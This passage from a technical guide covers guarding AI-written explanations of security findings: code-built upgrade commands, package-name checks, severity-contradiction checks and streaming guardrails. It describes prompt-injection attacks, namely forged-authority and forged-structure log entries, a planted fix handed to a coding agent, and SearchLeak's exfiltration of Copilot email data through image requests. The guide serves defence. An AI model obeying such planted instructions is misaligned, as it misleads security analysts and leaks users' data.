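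An attacker can also target the model that judges the text. The security company Trend Micro sent an encoded role-playing instruction to one model and passed the result to a second model for evaluation. Burton, Shala and Das report in *LLM as a Judge* that the second model started playing the role instead of giving a verdict. Code that rejects the text unless the judge returns a well-formed verdict limits the damage.

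### Building the upgrade command in code

A dependency scanner can avoid most of this by not letting the model write commands at all. The right command for acme-db depends on the package name and the fixed version, and the finding contains both. If acme-db is an npm package, the code could be:

```python
NAME = re.compile(r"(?:@[a-z0-9][a-z0-9._-]*/)?[a-z0-9][a-z0-9._-]*")
VERSION = re.compile(r"[0-9]+\.[0-9]+\.[0-9]+")

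def upgrade_command(finding):
    name = finding.get("package") or ""
    version = finding.get("fixed_version") or ""
    if not (NAME.fullmatch(name) and VERSION.fullmatch(version)):
        return None
    return ["npm", "install", f"{name}@{version}"]
```

The format checks matter because the package name comes from a project file that an outsider may have edited. In a shell, a semicolon in the name would start a second command, and npm would read a name beginning with a hyphen as an option. The function returns a list of arguments, so a program can run the command without a shell. The interface joins the list with spaces for display, which gives `npm install acme-db@2.3.4` for acme-db.

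The model still has a say in how the reader should proceed. Its reply already includes an upgrade-risk label, and code turns each label into a prewritten instruction:

| Label from the model | Instruction that code displays with the command |
|---|---|
| "low" | Upgrade acme-db from 2.3.0 to 2.3.4. |
| "high" or "unknown" | Upgrade acme-db from 2.3.0 to 2.3.4 in a test branch, and run the project's tests before merging. |

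If `upgrade_command` returns nothing, the tool shows "no fixed version listed" or the scanner's original text, without a command. A tool that handles other remedies can add an action field with values such as "upgrade", "change configuration" and "ask the owner". The code should offer the model only the actions the finding supports, and leave out "upgrade" when no fixed version exists.

An attacker who controls the model's reply can now choose only between the two instructions. The worst outcome is that the reader upgrades without testing and the application breaks. The explanation can also be filtered strictly, because if the check rejects a legitimate explanation for containing a command, the reader still gets the correct command from code.

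The template needs some facts about the project, such as its package manager, because projects that use Yarn or pnpm need a different command. If another package brings in acme-db, installing acme-db directly may leave the vulnerable copy in place, so the tool should name the package that depends on it rather than acme-db. Some scanners list several fixed versions in one field. The function rejects these values, but a team can add code that picks the lowest fixed version above the installed one.

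This approach doesn't cover every finding. A template can't write the code change needed to remove a SQL injection from the project's own code, for example. If the tool lets a model propose that change, the tool should show it as a code change for review, not as a command in the explanation. The approach also relies on the advisory, so if the advisory lists the wrong fixed version, the command will be wrong too.

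### Invented package names

Models sometimes recommend packages that don't exist. An attacker can register one of these package names and wait for people to install the package, which is called *slopsquatting*. *Bayesian-Calibrated Detection of Hallucinated Package Imports in AI-Assisted Code* (2026) credits the term to Seth Larson of the Python Software Foundation.

Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave the same roughly 40,000 programming questions about Python and JavaScript to five models: Claude Haiku 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 2.5 Pro, DeepSeek V3.2 and GPT-5.4-mini. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they mentioned did not exist. In 2024, an earlier team had found averages of 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones, so open models have improved much more than commercial ones. All five models invented 104 of the same names, and an attacker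 who registers one of these could reach users of every model.

The rates may differ for security explanations because the questions were general, GPT-5.4-mini ran with minimal reasoning, and none of the models could look anything up. Newer models may do better, but a tool that explains thousands of findings a day would still need a check if the rate were much lower.

A second model is a poor check because it has the same gaps in its knowledge. Burton and colleagues used GPT-4 to evaluate a response that recommended installing `mlj` as a Python package. GPT-4 did not catch that MLJ is a machine-learning framework for the language Julia. They replaced this check with a lookup in the package registry, the public database from which installers download packages.

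The lookup has to be careful. Churilov queried each registry in two ways, then repeated both queries at least 12 hours later. He counted a name as absent only if every query returned "not found", and treated timeouts and server errors as unknown. Earlier versions of the study used saved package lists from 2025, which lacked newer packages. They also counted correct Python import names as invented, because a module's name can differ from the name of the package that contains it. Fixing these and some smaller errors lowered every model's rate of invented names by about a fifth.

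A security tool doesn't need to repeat the lookup 12 hours later, since it can refuse a name whenever it is in doubt. The rules could be:

| Result for a package name in the model's text | Response |
|---|---|
| Not found | Refuse the text |
| Timeout, server error or conflicting answers | Refuse the text |
| Found, but new or with a malware record | Refuse the text and record the name for review |
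| Found, older, no malware record | Accept it only if the organization already uses or has approved the package |

The last row is strict because a package can exist and still be unsafe. Tenet's package existed, so a lookup alone would have accepted it. Of the 2,282 names that Churilov's models invented, 25 were registered within about six months, after a median of about three months, and at least one of these contained malware. An explanation with an invented name can therefore be harmless when the tool stores it but dangerous by the time someone reads it, which is a good reason to refuse it. Churilov also found at least 23 suggested names that had hosted malware before the registries removed it. The public database OSV keeps records of such packages.

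A company's private packages need an exception because they are not in the public registry. The tool should look for them in the company's own registry first. Looking them up in the public registry would reveal their names, and an attacker who registers one of those names there can sometimes get installers to fetch the attacker's package instead.

Planted text can also supply a made-up name. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) tested local coding models with ten prompts that asked for packages that don't exist. In one case the model tried to install the package under the requested name. In three others it chose a similar name that the study also treated as suspect, and in six it used real packages. Ten prompts are too few to estimate a rate, but the result shows that a check should cover the names the model writes as well as those in its input.

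When a dependency scanner reports the acme-db finding, the only package anyone should install is acme-db, and code already puts that name into the command. The registry check is for tools that let the model recommend a replacement package or a new library.

### When a coding agent reads the finding

An agent that fixes findings doesn't need the explanation. The tool can send it the finding's identifier, the permitted action and the argument list from `upgrade_command`, and show the explanation only to people. In the Seer attack, the coding agent received the planted fix as a trusted AI's conclusion, with nothing to show that an outsider had written it. If the tool sends only fields that code has filled in, the explanation can't carry a command to the agent. The tool still has to keep outsiders' text, such as the original error message, out of those fields.

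An agent that also reads other sources can still pick up a command from them. Tenet recommends that a person approve every command an agent wants to run, and the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises human approval before anyone executes a script from a model. Approval gives limited protection, because planted commands can look routine and people may click through frequent requests, as they do with frequent link warnings. The approval screen can help by comparing each command with the one built by code. It can let the user approve an exact match with one click, and show any other command with a note that it doesn't come from the finding.

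Tenet also recommends blocking agents' outbound network access by default, and says this alone would stop both the download and the data leak. It would stop the download only if the block covers the public package registry, because Tenet's test package was on npm. But an agent that upgrades dependencies has to download packages from somewhere. If the registry stays open, the block would still keep the agent from sending stolen credentials to an unknown server. To stop the download as well, a company can run its own registry of approved packages and make it the only address the agent can reach.

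## Checking that the text does not contradict the official severity

An explanation of acme-db can pass the length, link and command checks and still contain the words "this finding can safely be ignored" right below the correct HIGH label. The severity check looks for severity-override wording like this. It is the hardest of the four checks to build because misleading text, unlike a link or a command, can use any words and sometimes misleads by not mentioning the danger at all.

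### Forms of contradiction

| Form | Example for acme-db | What can expose it |
|---|---|---|
| Naming another level | "This is a low-severity issue." | The label |
| Telling the reader to ignore or postpone it | "You can leave this until the next major release." | The wording |
| Calling it a false positive | "The scanner has misread a safe query." | A review of the code |
| Claiming that someone approved it | "The security team has already accepted this risk." | The tool's own records |
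| Leaving out the attack | "acme-db handles the project's database queries." | The type of flaw in the finding |
| Exaggerating | "This is an emergency, so take the service offline now." | The label and the wording |

The model has no good reason to write about approvals. If someone has accepted the risk, the tool should have a record of the decision, and code can print it with a name and date. A claim by the model that a finding is a false positive is harder to handle because it may be right, but it should still go in a separate field rather than in the explanation.

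Models often exaggerate severity by mistake, which also does harm because each false alarm takes time to check. Du, Feng and colleagues (2026) report in *Reducing False Positives in Static Bug Detection with LLMs* that developers at Tencent, a large Chinese technology company, need 10 to 20 minutes to inspect one static-analysis warning.

The sentence "attackers are already using this flaw" can be true beside any severity label, even if it sounds exaggerated, because a CVSS base score describes the flaw and doesn't change when exploitation begins. The tool should look the flaw up in a list such as the Known Exploited Vulnerabilities catalog, which the US cybersecurity agency CISA maintains, and have code print the result. If the model makes the claim itself, the tool should reject the text.

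### A phrase list for each level

The simplest check searches the text for wording that doesn't fit the label. Software vendors already tie certain wording to certain levels. Microsoft's *Security Update Severity Rating System* recommends applying Critical updates immediately and Important ones at the earliest opportunity. For Moderate updates customers should consider applying them, and for Low ones they should evaluate whether to. Microsoft's four ratings don't line up exactly with the CVSS bands, but they suggest which advice is too weak or too strong for each level:

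```python
import re

ALWAYS = (r"ignored?|harmless|benign|no action|false (?:positive|alarm)|"
          r"whitelisted|already (?:approved|accepted)")
REFUSED = {
    "LOW":      r"medium|high|critical|immediately|urgent(?:ly)?|emergency",
    "MEDIUM":   r"low|high|critical|immediately|emergency|can wait",
    "HIGH":     r"low|medium|critical|emergency|can wait|consider updating",
    "CRITICAL": r"low|medium|high|can wait|consider updating",
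}

def severity_wording(text, label):
    return re.findall(rf"\b(?:{ALWAYS}|{REFUSED[label]})\b", text, re.I)
```

Suppose the model writes an accurate sentence about acme-db, "acme-db 2.3.0 has a SQL injection flaw that lets any logged-in user read or change the database", and then adds one of four others. With the label HIGH, the function finds these matches:

| Added sentence | Match | Result |
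|---|---|---|
| "This finding can safely be ignored." | "ignored" | Correct refusal |
| "The attack complexity is low." | "low" | False block |
| "This is not a low-risk issue." | "low" | False block |
| "The flagged queries are routine database traffic." | None | Missed violation |

A *missed violation* is a text that breaks a rule but passes the check.

The sentence about attack complexity is true and supports the HIGH label, since the *CVSS v3.1 Base Score Calculator* rates low complexity as the worst value. If the complexity were high, acme-db's score would fall from 8.8 to 7.5. A team can avoid this false block by counting a level word only when it stands next to "severity", "risk" or "priority", but the narrower pattern would miss "the danger here is low".

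Negation causes both wrong rejections and wrong acceptances. For a HIGH finding, the function rejects "this is not a low-risk issue", which agrees with the label, but accepts "this is not a high-risk issue", which contradicts it, because "high" is a permitted word. Looking for "not" nearby helps with these two sentences but fails on "hardly a high-risk issue" and "nobody would call this high-risk".

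A stricter rule avoids most of this. Code already covers the label and the CVSS metrics, so the prompt can instruct the model not to mention severity, priority or CVSS values. The tool then rejects any level word next to "severity", "risk", "priority" or "complexity", whichever level it is and even if the sentence negates it. The two harmless sentences still fail, but the model was told not to write them and can usually leave them out when the tool prompts it again. Texts like the one about routine traffic still get through.

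### The log-injection experiment

Attackers can make a model write such texts. In their May 2026 experiment, Pandey and Bhujang gave logs to gpt-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, and hid an instruction in every malicious one. They tested four kinds of instruction:

- A direct override tells the model to disregard its earlier instructions.
- Forged authority claims to come from an administrator who has cleared the entry.
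- Forged structure imitates the end of the log, followed by a finished verdict.
- Fake encoding dresses an instruction up as encoded data.

The model's three tasks were classifying each log, summarizing it and recommending a response. Pandey and Bhujang also compared four levels of defense. With no defense, the software put the fields straight into the prompt. The structured defense wrapped each field in tags and told the model that the contents were untrusted data. The sanitized defense added a filter that removed suspicious keywords from the fields. The constrained defense kept the tags and limited the output to fixed labels or templates.

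The experiment combined four kinds of instruction, four defenses and three tasks into 48 conditions, each with 200 synthetic logs, 120 of them malicious. The malicious logs showed attacks such as SQL injection, path traversal and password guessing with stolen credentials. In each malicious log, the software added the instruction to one randomly chosen field that an outsider could write to, such as the user agent. It left the 80 benign logs unchanged.

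For summaries, Pandey and Bhujang counted an attack as successful if the summary accepted the planted instruction, omitted the attack or concluded, contrary to the log, that the activity was benign.

| Planted text | No defense | Structured | Sanitized | Constrained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct override | 7% | 5% | 15% | 0% |
| Forged authority | 49% | 44% | 35% | 24% |
| Forged structure | 96% | 75% | 27% | 38% |
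| Fake encoding | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Forged structure produced no explicit "benign" labels under any defense, though it corrupted up to 96% of the summaries. Without defenses, forged authority corrupted 49% of the summaries, and 7% of all summaries contained a "benign" label. A filter that looked only for that label would have caught at most about one in seven of the corrupted summaries.

A phrase list can include wording beyond that label, such as "no action". It would catch some of the corrupted summaries, but Pandey and Bhujang don't report how many advised no action and how many only softened or omitted the attack, so its miss rate is unknown. It can't catch a summary that leaves the attack out, because that summary contains no forbidden phrase. To catch softened descriptions, it would need to include every mild way of describing an intrusion. An attacker who knows or guesses the list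 can also ask for wording that isn't on it.

Pandey and Bhujang's example of forged structure casts some doubt on the 0% figure, because it says that the entry "has been classified as benign", which looks like an explicit label. They may have scored labels by a narrower rule than a reader would use. Their main point still holds, since a few misclassified summaries could not explain the gap between 0% and 96%.

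With constrained output, the remaining 38% came from the model picking a reassuring template for a real attack. A tool that has the severity label can prevent this by not offering reassuring templates for HIGH findings.

Forged authority was the most effective attack on classification. It made the model label 68% of the malicious logs benign without defenses, 33% with constrained output, 22% with the keyword filter and 15% with the structured defense. When the model recommended a response, forged structure led it to advise against action in 39% of cases without defenses and 10% with constrained output. Direct overrides never changed a classification, although a simulator that Pandey and Bhujang built from older research had predicted that they would succeed 92% of the time without defenses.

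The rates describe one small model at one time, and current models probably resist these instructions better. The logs came from templates, so they lacked the cut-off fields and odd formatting of real logs. Those features could make an attack easier or harder. With 120 malicious logs per condition, the margin of error is about 7 to 9 percentage points. The attacker also couldn't see a summary and try again. The experiment did not include a run without planted text, but fake encoding never succeeded, which suggests that the model rarely played down an attack on its own.

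The setting also differs from a dependency scanner because only gpt-4o-mini analyzed the logs, so its summary had no official label to contradict. A severity check helps with logs only if another detector has already raised an alert on them.

### Asking a model about contradictions

An *entailment model* is a classifier that takes two texts, a premise and a hypothesis, and estimates whether the premise implies the hypothesis, contradicts it or does neither. For acme-db, code can write the premise from the finding: "acme-db 2.3.0 has a SQL injection flaw. Its severity is HIGH. The project should upgrade to 2.3.4." Each sentence of the explanation is a hypothesis.

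"This finding can safely be ignored" contradicts the premise, and a good model should label it that way. "The flagged queries are routine database traffic" would probably be labeled neither contradicted nor implied, because a package can have a flaw and still carry routine traffic. A check that refuses only contradictions would accept it. Refusing every sentence that the premise doesn't imply would catch it, but would also refuse most of what the AI-written text is meant to add, such as which part of the project uses acme-db.

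*Decomposed Entailment for Factuality Checking and Hallucination Detection* (Oukelmoun, Semmar and De Chalendar, 2026) tests entailment on news summaries that people had checked against the articles. Comparing the whole summary with the whole article gave a precision of 0.83 but a recall (the share of faulty summaries caught) of only 0.52. The paper's own system, HallDetect, splits the summary into claims, compares each with pieces of the article in five sizes, and flags the summary if any claim fails. This raised recall to between 0.96 and 1.00 but lowered precision to between 0.58 and 0.64.

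Checking claim by claim found nearly every faulty summary, but about four in ten of its flags were wrong, and on summaries of dialogue roughly four in five were. The two methods also divide the article differently, so the test doesn't show how much of the gain came from splitting the summary. The systems used compressed models from 2024 that run on a home computer.

Newer checkers do better. The LLM-AggreFact benchmark has 29,320 claims in its test set, each paired with a document and a human judgment on whether the document supports the claim. Hobbs and Hinson (2026), in *GauntletScore*, compared two fast commercial models, a general frontier model and their own system, which combines all three. Their company sells the system. On a sample of 2,992 claims, the results were:

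| Checker | Supported claims accepted | Unsupported claims caught | Average of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast model A | 89.5% | 67.8% | 78.7% |
| Fast model B | 89.0% | 66.6% | 77.8% |
| Frontier model | 79.7% | 79.5% | 79.6% |
| All three combined | 82.5% | 77.5% | 80.0% |

The checkers' averages are close, but they make different mistakes. Suppose a tool writes 1,000 explanations a day, each with one claim about severity, and 20 of them understate it. If the benchmark rates applied, fast model A would catch about 14 of the 20 and reject about 100 harmless texts, while the frontier model would catch about 16 and reject about 200. Real explanations contain several sentences, so there could be more false rejections. However, a direct "safe to ignore" is easier to spot than the errors in this benchmark, which are often one wrong detail in an otherwise good summary.

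Giving the checker more time to reason may not help. *Jev-as-a-Judge for RAG Claim Verification* (2026) tested a frontier model, Astra, on 495 claims from the same benchmark. Averaged over the eleven datasets, Astra scored 73.8 at low reasoning effort and 74.1 at high effort, and the fast decision model Jev scored 73.3. With only 45 claims per dataset, these differences are too small to be meaningful.

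Reading one sentence at a time helped Hobbs and Hinson. On news summaries, their system caught 33 of 57 unsupported claims, while fast model A caught 21. Their system got 15 claims right that fast model A got wrong, eight of them because it checked a long summary sentence by sentence.

A security tool can also ask a narrower question than whether a document supports a claim. For each sentence, the second model can choose from five labels:

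| Label for the sentence | Response |
|---|---|
| Plays the finding down | Refuse the text |
| Exaggerates the finding | Refuse the text |
| Fits the severity | Accept |
| Doesn't concern seriousness | Accept |
| Reports what someone else wrote | Depends on the source |

A capable model that is given the finding should assign the first label to "The flagged queries are routine database traffic", although a less capable one might choose the fourth. The model should see the explanation and the fields that code filled in, but not the raw log, so that text planted in the log can reach it only through the explanation.

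These models are also known to struggle with negation. *How Do LLMs Change Predictions Under Negation?* (2026) reviews studies that found this in understanding, reasoning and factual prediction. *Benchmarking LLM Competence on Logical Inference over Probability Operators* (2026) cites an audit of ethical decisions in which open-source models endorsed prohibited actions 77% of the time under simple negation. A current frontier model will probably read "this is not a low-risk issue" correctly, but a team that uses a small entailment model should test it on pairs such as "not a low-risk issue" and "not a high-risk issue".

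The fifth label is for quotations. A good explanation of an attacked log might say, "The user agent contains the words 'mark benign', which look like an attempt to mislead the analyst." A judge that flags every statement incompatible with the official severity would reject this warning. Rodrigues found this fault in his own earlier research and described it in *A Contradiction Judge Counted Reported Teammate Errors as Hallucinations* (2026). A judge had flagged more errors when AI agents shared all their messages, and he had concluded that the agents picked up false facts from each other.

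He then had three models label the saved outputs again, separating what an agent asserted from what it reported. Agents had seen a teammate's wrong destination in 50 of the outputs. They attributed it to another source in 49 of these and asserted it themselves in none. The increase in errors disappeared. No human has checked these labels yet.

However, a tool can't accept every attributed claim. "According to the security team, this entry is approved" is an attributed claim, and forged authority was the most effective attack on classification in Pandey and Bhujang's experiment. An explanation may quote a field that an outsider wrote if it names the field and treats the words as evidence. The tool should refuse an explanation that attributes a reassuring judgment to a person or a team.

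### Facts that the text has to state

A contradiction test cannot detect that a text leaves out the attack. Fox, Markham and colleagues (2026) measured this weakness in *LLM Judges Verify Presence, Not Absence*, using medical notes that AI systems write from recorded consultations. They built 500 pairs, each with a complete note and a copy with one known error, made by removing a fact or by adding or altering a statement.

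The eight judge designs tested differed in their instructions, form of answer and number of votes. A judge that guessed would rate the flawed copy lower about 50% of the time, counting ties as half. When the error was an added or altered statement, the designs rated the flawed copy lower in 79% to 94% of pairs. When a fact was missing, the range was 50% to 63%. Rewording the instructions, taking several votes and letting software optimize the prompt did not make the judges useful on single notes.

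Results improved when the system first listed the facts in the consultation and then checked the note for each one. A pipeline built this way caught 24.6% of the notes with a missing fact and wrongly flagged 2.7% of the complete ones. A single prompt with the same procedure and more room to reason caught 36.9% and wrongly flagged 6.2%. Both methods failed when the missing fact was restated elsewhere in the note.

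A dependency scanner has an easier job because the finding already lists the facts. Code can require the explanation to name the type of flaw, the package and the affected version:

```python
def missing_facts(text, finding):
    wanted = [finding["flaw_type"], finding["package"], finding["version"]]
    return [fact for fact in wanted
            if not re.search(rf"(?<![\w.-]){re.escape(fact)}(?![\w-]|\.\w)", text, re.I)]
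```

The conditions around the fact stop `2.3.0` from matching inside `12.3.0`. If the whole explanation of acme-db is "The flagged queries are routine database traffic", the tool rejects it because all three facts are missing.

This search works because package names and version numbers have one spelling. It is nearly useless for facts that a writer can phrase in many ways. *COVERAGE-TRACE* (Karkehabadi, Hassanpour and Banchs, 2026) tested 80 pairs of meeting summaries. In each pair, one summary included a given fact and the other did not. Exact matching scored an AUROC of 0.512, where 0.5 means guessing and 1.0 means perfect separation, and the best entailment baseline scored 0.640.

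The paper's own method changes a fact in the source, for example from "three quarters" to "two thirds", and measures how much less likely a model then finds the same summary. A summary that states the original fact should become much less likely. The method scored between 0.764 and 0.825, but only 0.59 to 0.62 after a correction for wording changes that keep the meaning. For acme-db, it is easier to tell the model in the prompt to use the exact term "SQL injection". Code can also accept a few synonyms such as "SQLi".

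The list of required facts should be short. Fox and colleagues tested one method that checked about 62 facts per consultation, and it flagged 98.7% of the complete notes because no real note contains every detail. Models are also poor at deciding alone which facts matter. Two frontier models grading the same details agreed barely more often than chance (Cohen's kappa of 0.18), while a different pair of graders with a written rubric reached 0.66. The team should therefore choose the facts for each type of finding once and write them down.

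For log summaries, the required facts can be the attack type and source address of each alert that other detectors raised. Without such alerts, someone has to decide which log lines matter. *OmitEHR* (Lin, 2026) trains a model on summaries that doctors wrote before AI tools were common, to predict which sentences in a medical record belong in its summary and flag important ones that are missing. A security team with years of incident reports could try the same approach, but would have to make sure that past analysts hadn't routinely left out the attacks the team wants to catch.

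Checking for required facts doesn't catch a denial. "acme-db 2.3.0 is not affected by SQL injection" contains all three facts and passes. The same four sentences show why a tool needs more than one method. This table again assumes that each one follows the accurate sentence about acme-db. The column for the second model shows what a capable model should do, not a measured result.

| Added sentence | Right answer | Phrase list | Second model | Required facts |
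|---|---|---|---|---|
| "This finding can safely be ignored." | Refuse | Refuses | Refuses | Accepts |
| "The attack complexity is low." | Accept | Refuses | Accepts | Accepts |
| "This is not a low-risk issue." | Accept | Refuses | Accepts | Accepts |
| "The flagged queries are routine database traffic." | Refuse | Accepts | Refuses | Accepts, unless it replaces the accurate sentence |

The phrase list and the fact check need almost no computing time, so they should run first, and the second model should read only the texts that pass both. Refusing a text when any one of the three checks flags it catches the most contradictions, but it also blocks every correct text that any of them flags by mistake.

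### When the label is wrong

The model is sometimes right when it disagrees with the label. Du and colleagues collected 433 warnings from Tencent's own static-analysis tool, of which 328 were false alarms. The best method they tested, which combines a language model with further static analysis, removed 94% to 98% of the false alarms and kept most of the real bugs. The model-based methods took 2 to 110 seconds to check each warning, at a cost of at most 12 cents. The study covered three kinds of programming bug, not severity ratings, and nobody was trying to fool the model. Even so, a tool that discards every disagreement would lose useful information.

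A severity label can also be correct in general but wrong for a particular project. Microsoft rates a flaw by its worst theoretical outcome, treats the likelihood of exploitation separately, and encourages customers to evaluate their own environments. If acme-db is only in a test program that runs on one developer's machine, HIGH may overstate the danger. But the tool can't let a model lower the label, because an attacker who can influence the model would use it to lower the label.

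The model can report disagreement with the official severity in a separate field with a fixed set of values, such as "none", "label seems too high", "label seems too low" and "possible false positive". Code should accept a value other than "none" only if the model cites evidence that the tool can find, such as a file path in the project or a line of code. The disagreement then goes to a reviewer, while the screen still shows the official label. The reviewer should see the cited file or line, because the model's argument may have come from an attacker.

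If the reviewer agrees, the official label changes through a recorded decision. GitLab, a platform for storing and testing code, has such a process. Its *Vulnerability management policy* lets an organization write rules that set a finding's severity to a given level, or raise or lower it by one level. A rule matches findings by file path, directory or identifier. By default, only the owner of a project or group can create the project that holds these policies. A new policy takes effect after someone reviews and merges it. When a rule changes a severity, GitLab adds a note to the finding's record.

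GitLab's *5 ways to fix misleading vulnerability severities with policy* (2026) explains that developers can't change or disable these policies, and that an authorized user's manual change takes precedence over them. The design document, GitLab's *Automated Vulnerability Severity Overrides/Customization Policy*, calls for a visible marker next to every changed severity and an audit entry with the time, the author and the change. GitLab's *Manual Vulnerability Severity Overrides* explains that the entry for a manual change names the old level, the new level and the user. Later scans don't overwrite the manual change.

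A rule also applies to findings that nobody has seen yet. If a team lowers the severity of every SQL injection in an `internal` folder because acme-db is harmless there, the next SQL injection found in that folder will also start one level lower. If the team disagrees with the severity of only one finding, changing that finding manually is safer. A team that wants a rule should make it match the specific vulnerability as well as the folder.

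Lowering the severity is usually better than dismissing the finding, because a lowered finding stays in the queue. If the reviewer decides that the finding is false, they can dismiss it in GitLab with a fixed reason, such as "False positive", "Acceptable risk" or "Used in tests". Reviewers can also use the recorded reason to check a claim in a later text that the team accepted the risk.

Two parts of the acme-db tool need to handle the change. The merge code compares the severity with the score, so a label lowered to MEDIUM beside a score of 8.8 would look like an error. It should compare the score with the scanner's original label instead. The severity check should use the new label and run again on the stored explanation, because a sentence that fitted HIGH, such as "upgrade at the earliest opportunity", may now be too strong. The screen can show "MEDIUM, lowered from HIGH" with the reviewer's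 name and the date, all copied from the audit record.

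## Showing only checked text and handling failures

The tool must show readers only text that has passed the four checks, and it needs something else to show when a text fails. Using the functions from the earlier sections, the whole sequence could look like this:

```python
RETRY = {"length", "address", "command", "level word", "missing fact"}
LEVELS = {"low", "medium", "high", "critical"}

def problems(text, finding):
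    found = set()
    if len(text) > 600:
        found.add("length")
    if has_address(text, [finding["location"]]):
        found.add("address")
    if EXECUTABLE.search(text):
        found.add("required command" if OBLIGATION.search(text) else "command")
    for hit in severity_wording(text, finding["severity"]):
        found.add("level word" if hit.lower() in LEVELS else "severity")
    if missing_facts(text, finding):
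        found.add("missing fact")
    return found or judge(text, finding)        # second model; returns a set of faults

def explain(finding):
    for attempt in (1, 2):
        reply = complete_reply(finding, attempt)     # waits for the end of the reply
        try:
            text = clean(parse(reply)["explanation"])
            found = problems(text, finding)
        except ValueError:                           # unfinished, malformed or refused characters
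            found = {"unreadable"}
        if not found:
            return publish(finding, text)            # stores the text, then shows it
        log_refusal(finding, attempt, found, reply)
        if not found <= RETRY:
            break
    return publish(finding, fallback(finding))
```

The second model again runs only on texts that pass every other check. If it is down or returns no usable verdict, `judge` reports a fault that is not in `RETRY`, so the reader gets the fallback text.

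The code runs all the checks that take little compute, even after one fails. The acme-db explanation is too long, so the code would normally ask for a shorter version. If it stopped at the length check, it would ask a possibly manipulated model for another draft without noticing the "required action" further down. The code also doesn't ask again after an unreadable reply, because it can't tell what else was in it.

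### One text for checking and display

The tool has to display the cleaned text byte for byte as it was checked, because the results apply only to that exact string.

Escaping text for a web page changes the bytes in transit, for example from `<` to `&lt;`, but the browser turns them back into the same characters. Converting the text is riskier. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* explains that when a library cleans HTML and returns a string, the browser has to parse that string again and can get a different result. Plain text avoids this.

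The tool can store a hash of the checked text and, before each display, compare it with a new hash of the text it is about to show. This catches accidental changes, such as a database cutting long fields, but not changes by an attacker who can rewrite both the text and the stored hash.

All text shown on screen has to go through the same function. Cybernews' *Claude Code's preview pane could leak your secrets* describes a flaw in Anthropic's desktop coding tool, which displayed HTML files larger than 256 KB by a different route from smaller ones, where scripts in the file could run without the usual protections. In the acme-db tool, `publish` should be the only code that can display a new explanation, and later page views should read the copy `publish` stored.

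The same bytes can look different if someone else controls the display. Paz's *Poisoned Typeface* describes a web page with a custom font that showed the reader dangerous instructions while the underlying text was harmless fan fiction. None of the 11 AI assistants that his company tested in December 2025 noticed. A security tool should use its own fonts and styles for explanations.

### SearchLeak

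Checking the text after displaying it can be too late even if the delay is only a few seconds. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on the enterprise search in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which looks through a company's emails, calendars and files. Its identifier is CVE-2026-42824. The attack took one click:

1. The victim clicks a link to a real Microsoft address. The search text inside the address contains the attacker's instructions, which Copilot follows.
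2. Copilot finds an email and writes an image tag with the email's subject in the image's address.
3. The browser processes the tag while the answer is still arriving, and requests the image.
4. Copilot finishes the answer. Microsoft's filter then wraps it in a code block, so that the browser shows the tag as text, but the request has already gone out.

The page's content security policy blocked images from unknown hosts but allowed bing.com. Bing's search-by-image service accepts a picture's address, and Microsoft's servers then fetch the picture. The browser therefore contacted only Bing, which passed the subject line to the attacker's server. A subject line can contain a login code, and Varonis warns that the attack could also reach meeting details and company files.

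Microsoft published *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) on 4 June, eleven days before Varonis's account. Microsoft lists the flaw as fully mitigated on its side and not exploited. It rates the flaw Critical, although the CVSS score of 6.5 is in the Medium band.

The filter worked, since the browser treated the image tag as plain text once the code block was in place. If Copilot had held the answer back until then, the browser would never have requested the image. Removing Bing from the policy would have closed only this route, since EchoLeak used a Teams service for the same purpose. Varonis recommends sanitizing text when it is rendered, not afterwards, and reviewing every permitted domain that fetches user-supplied addresses.

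### Holding back the stream

Many applications *stream* a reply, showing each piece as the model writes it, so users wait less for the first words. In a test of 20 requests to GPT-4o, reported in NVIDIA's *Working with Streaming Output*, the first words arrived after 0.55 seconds on average with streaming and 3.68 seconds without.

That test used the default setting of NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails toolkit, which sends each piece to the user before checking it. NVIDIA's *Output Rail Streaming Configuration* lists a default piece size of 200 tokens. A 600-character explanation is roughly 150 tokens, so the reader would have all of it before any check ran. Setting `stream_first` to false makes the toolkit check each piece before sending it.

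Other products have different defaults:

- AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes a default mode for Amazon Bedrock that checks each piece before release. The optional asynchronous mode shows text immediately and cannot mask sensitive information.
- Microsoft's *Content streaming* also describes checking first as the default. With the asynchronous filter, the warning can arrive up to about 1,000 characters after the offending text.
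- Portkey's *Handle streaming output guardrails for client-side decisions* describes a service that checks a streamed reply only after it ends. The service doesn't retry or block anything, and leaves that to the developer's own code.

A compromise is to check the text one complete sentence at a time. *SentGuard* (Yu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) keeps new text in a hidden buffer and releases each sentence only after a small model has checked everything written so far. The main model writes the next sentence during each check, so most of the checking adds no delay. In simulated replays with about 16 sentence pieces per reply, this added 36 milliseconds in total at ordinary speeds, compared with 576 if the main model paused for every check.

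SentGuard caught 90.5% of unsafe replies within two sentences and wrongly flagged 7.41% of safe ones. The tests covered harmful content in general, not text that plays down a security finding. *Predict, Don't React* (2026) notes that buffered text appears at about the checker's speed if the checker is slower than the model.

Pattern searches can miss a forbidden phrase that starts in one piece of text and ends in the next, so NVIDIA's toolkit repeats the last 50 tokens to catch such cases. Frost (2026) points out in *Withholding the Completing Chunk* that no fixed overlap is enough for a pattern that can span any distance. Frost's method remembers how far each pattern has matched and withholds the piece that completes it. Its Python and TypeScript versions agreed with a full search of the text in all of about 200,000 test cases.

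Even an exact method has to accept or reject text before the next letter arrives, so if one piece ends in "low" and the next begins with "er", a search for the word "low" rejects a text that says "lower". Frost's method also matches only fixed patterns, so it misses paraphrases and look-alike letters.

Two of the acme-db checks need the whole text, because the tool can't measure the final length or identify missing facts until the text is complete. Later text can also change the meaning of earlier text. For example, "This finding is safe to ignore" might be followed by "That is what an attacker wants you to think." If the tool shows text as it is generated and a check fails halfway through, the reader has already seen the beginning.

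The tool should hold back a short explanation until the whole text has been checked. At 40 tokens per second, 150 tokens take just under four seconds, while the first sentence might be ready in a quarter of a second. A dependency scanner can write its explanations during the scan, so nobody has to wait for them. A log viewer with an "explain" button can show the severity and the other copied fields at once, with a progress indicator where the explanation will go. Nalpas (2026), in Google's guidance for Chrome developers, also suggests not streaming short outputs.

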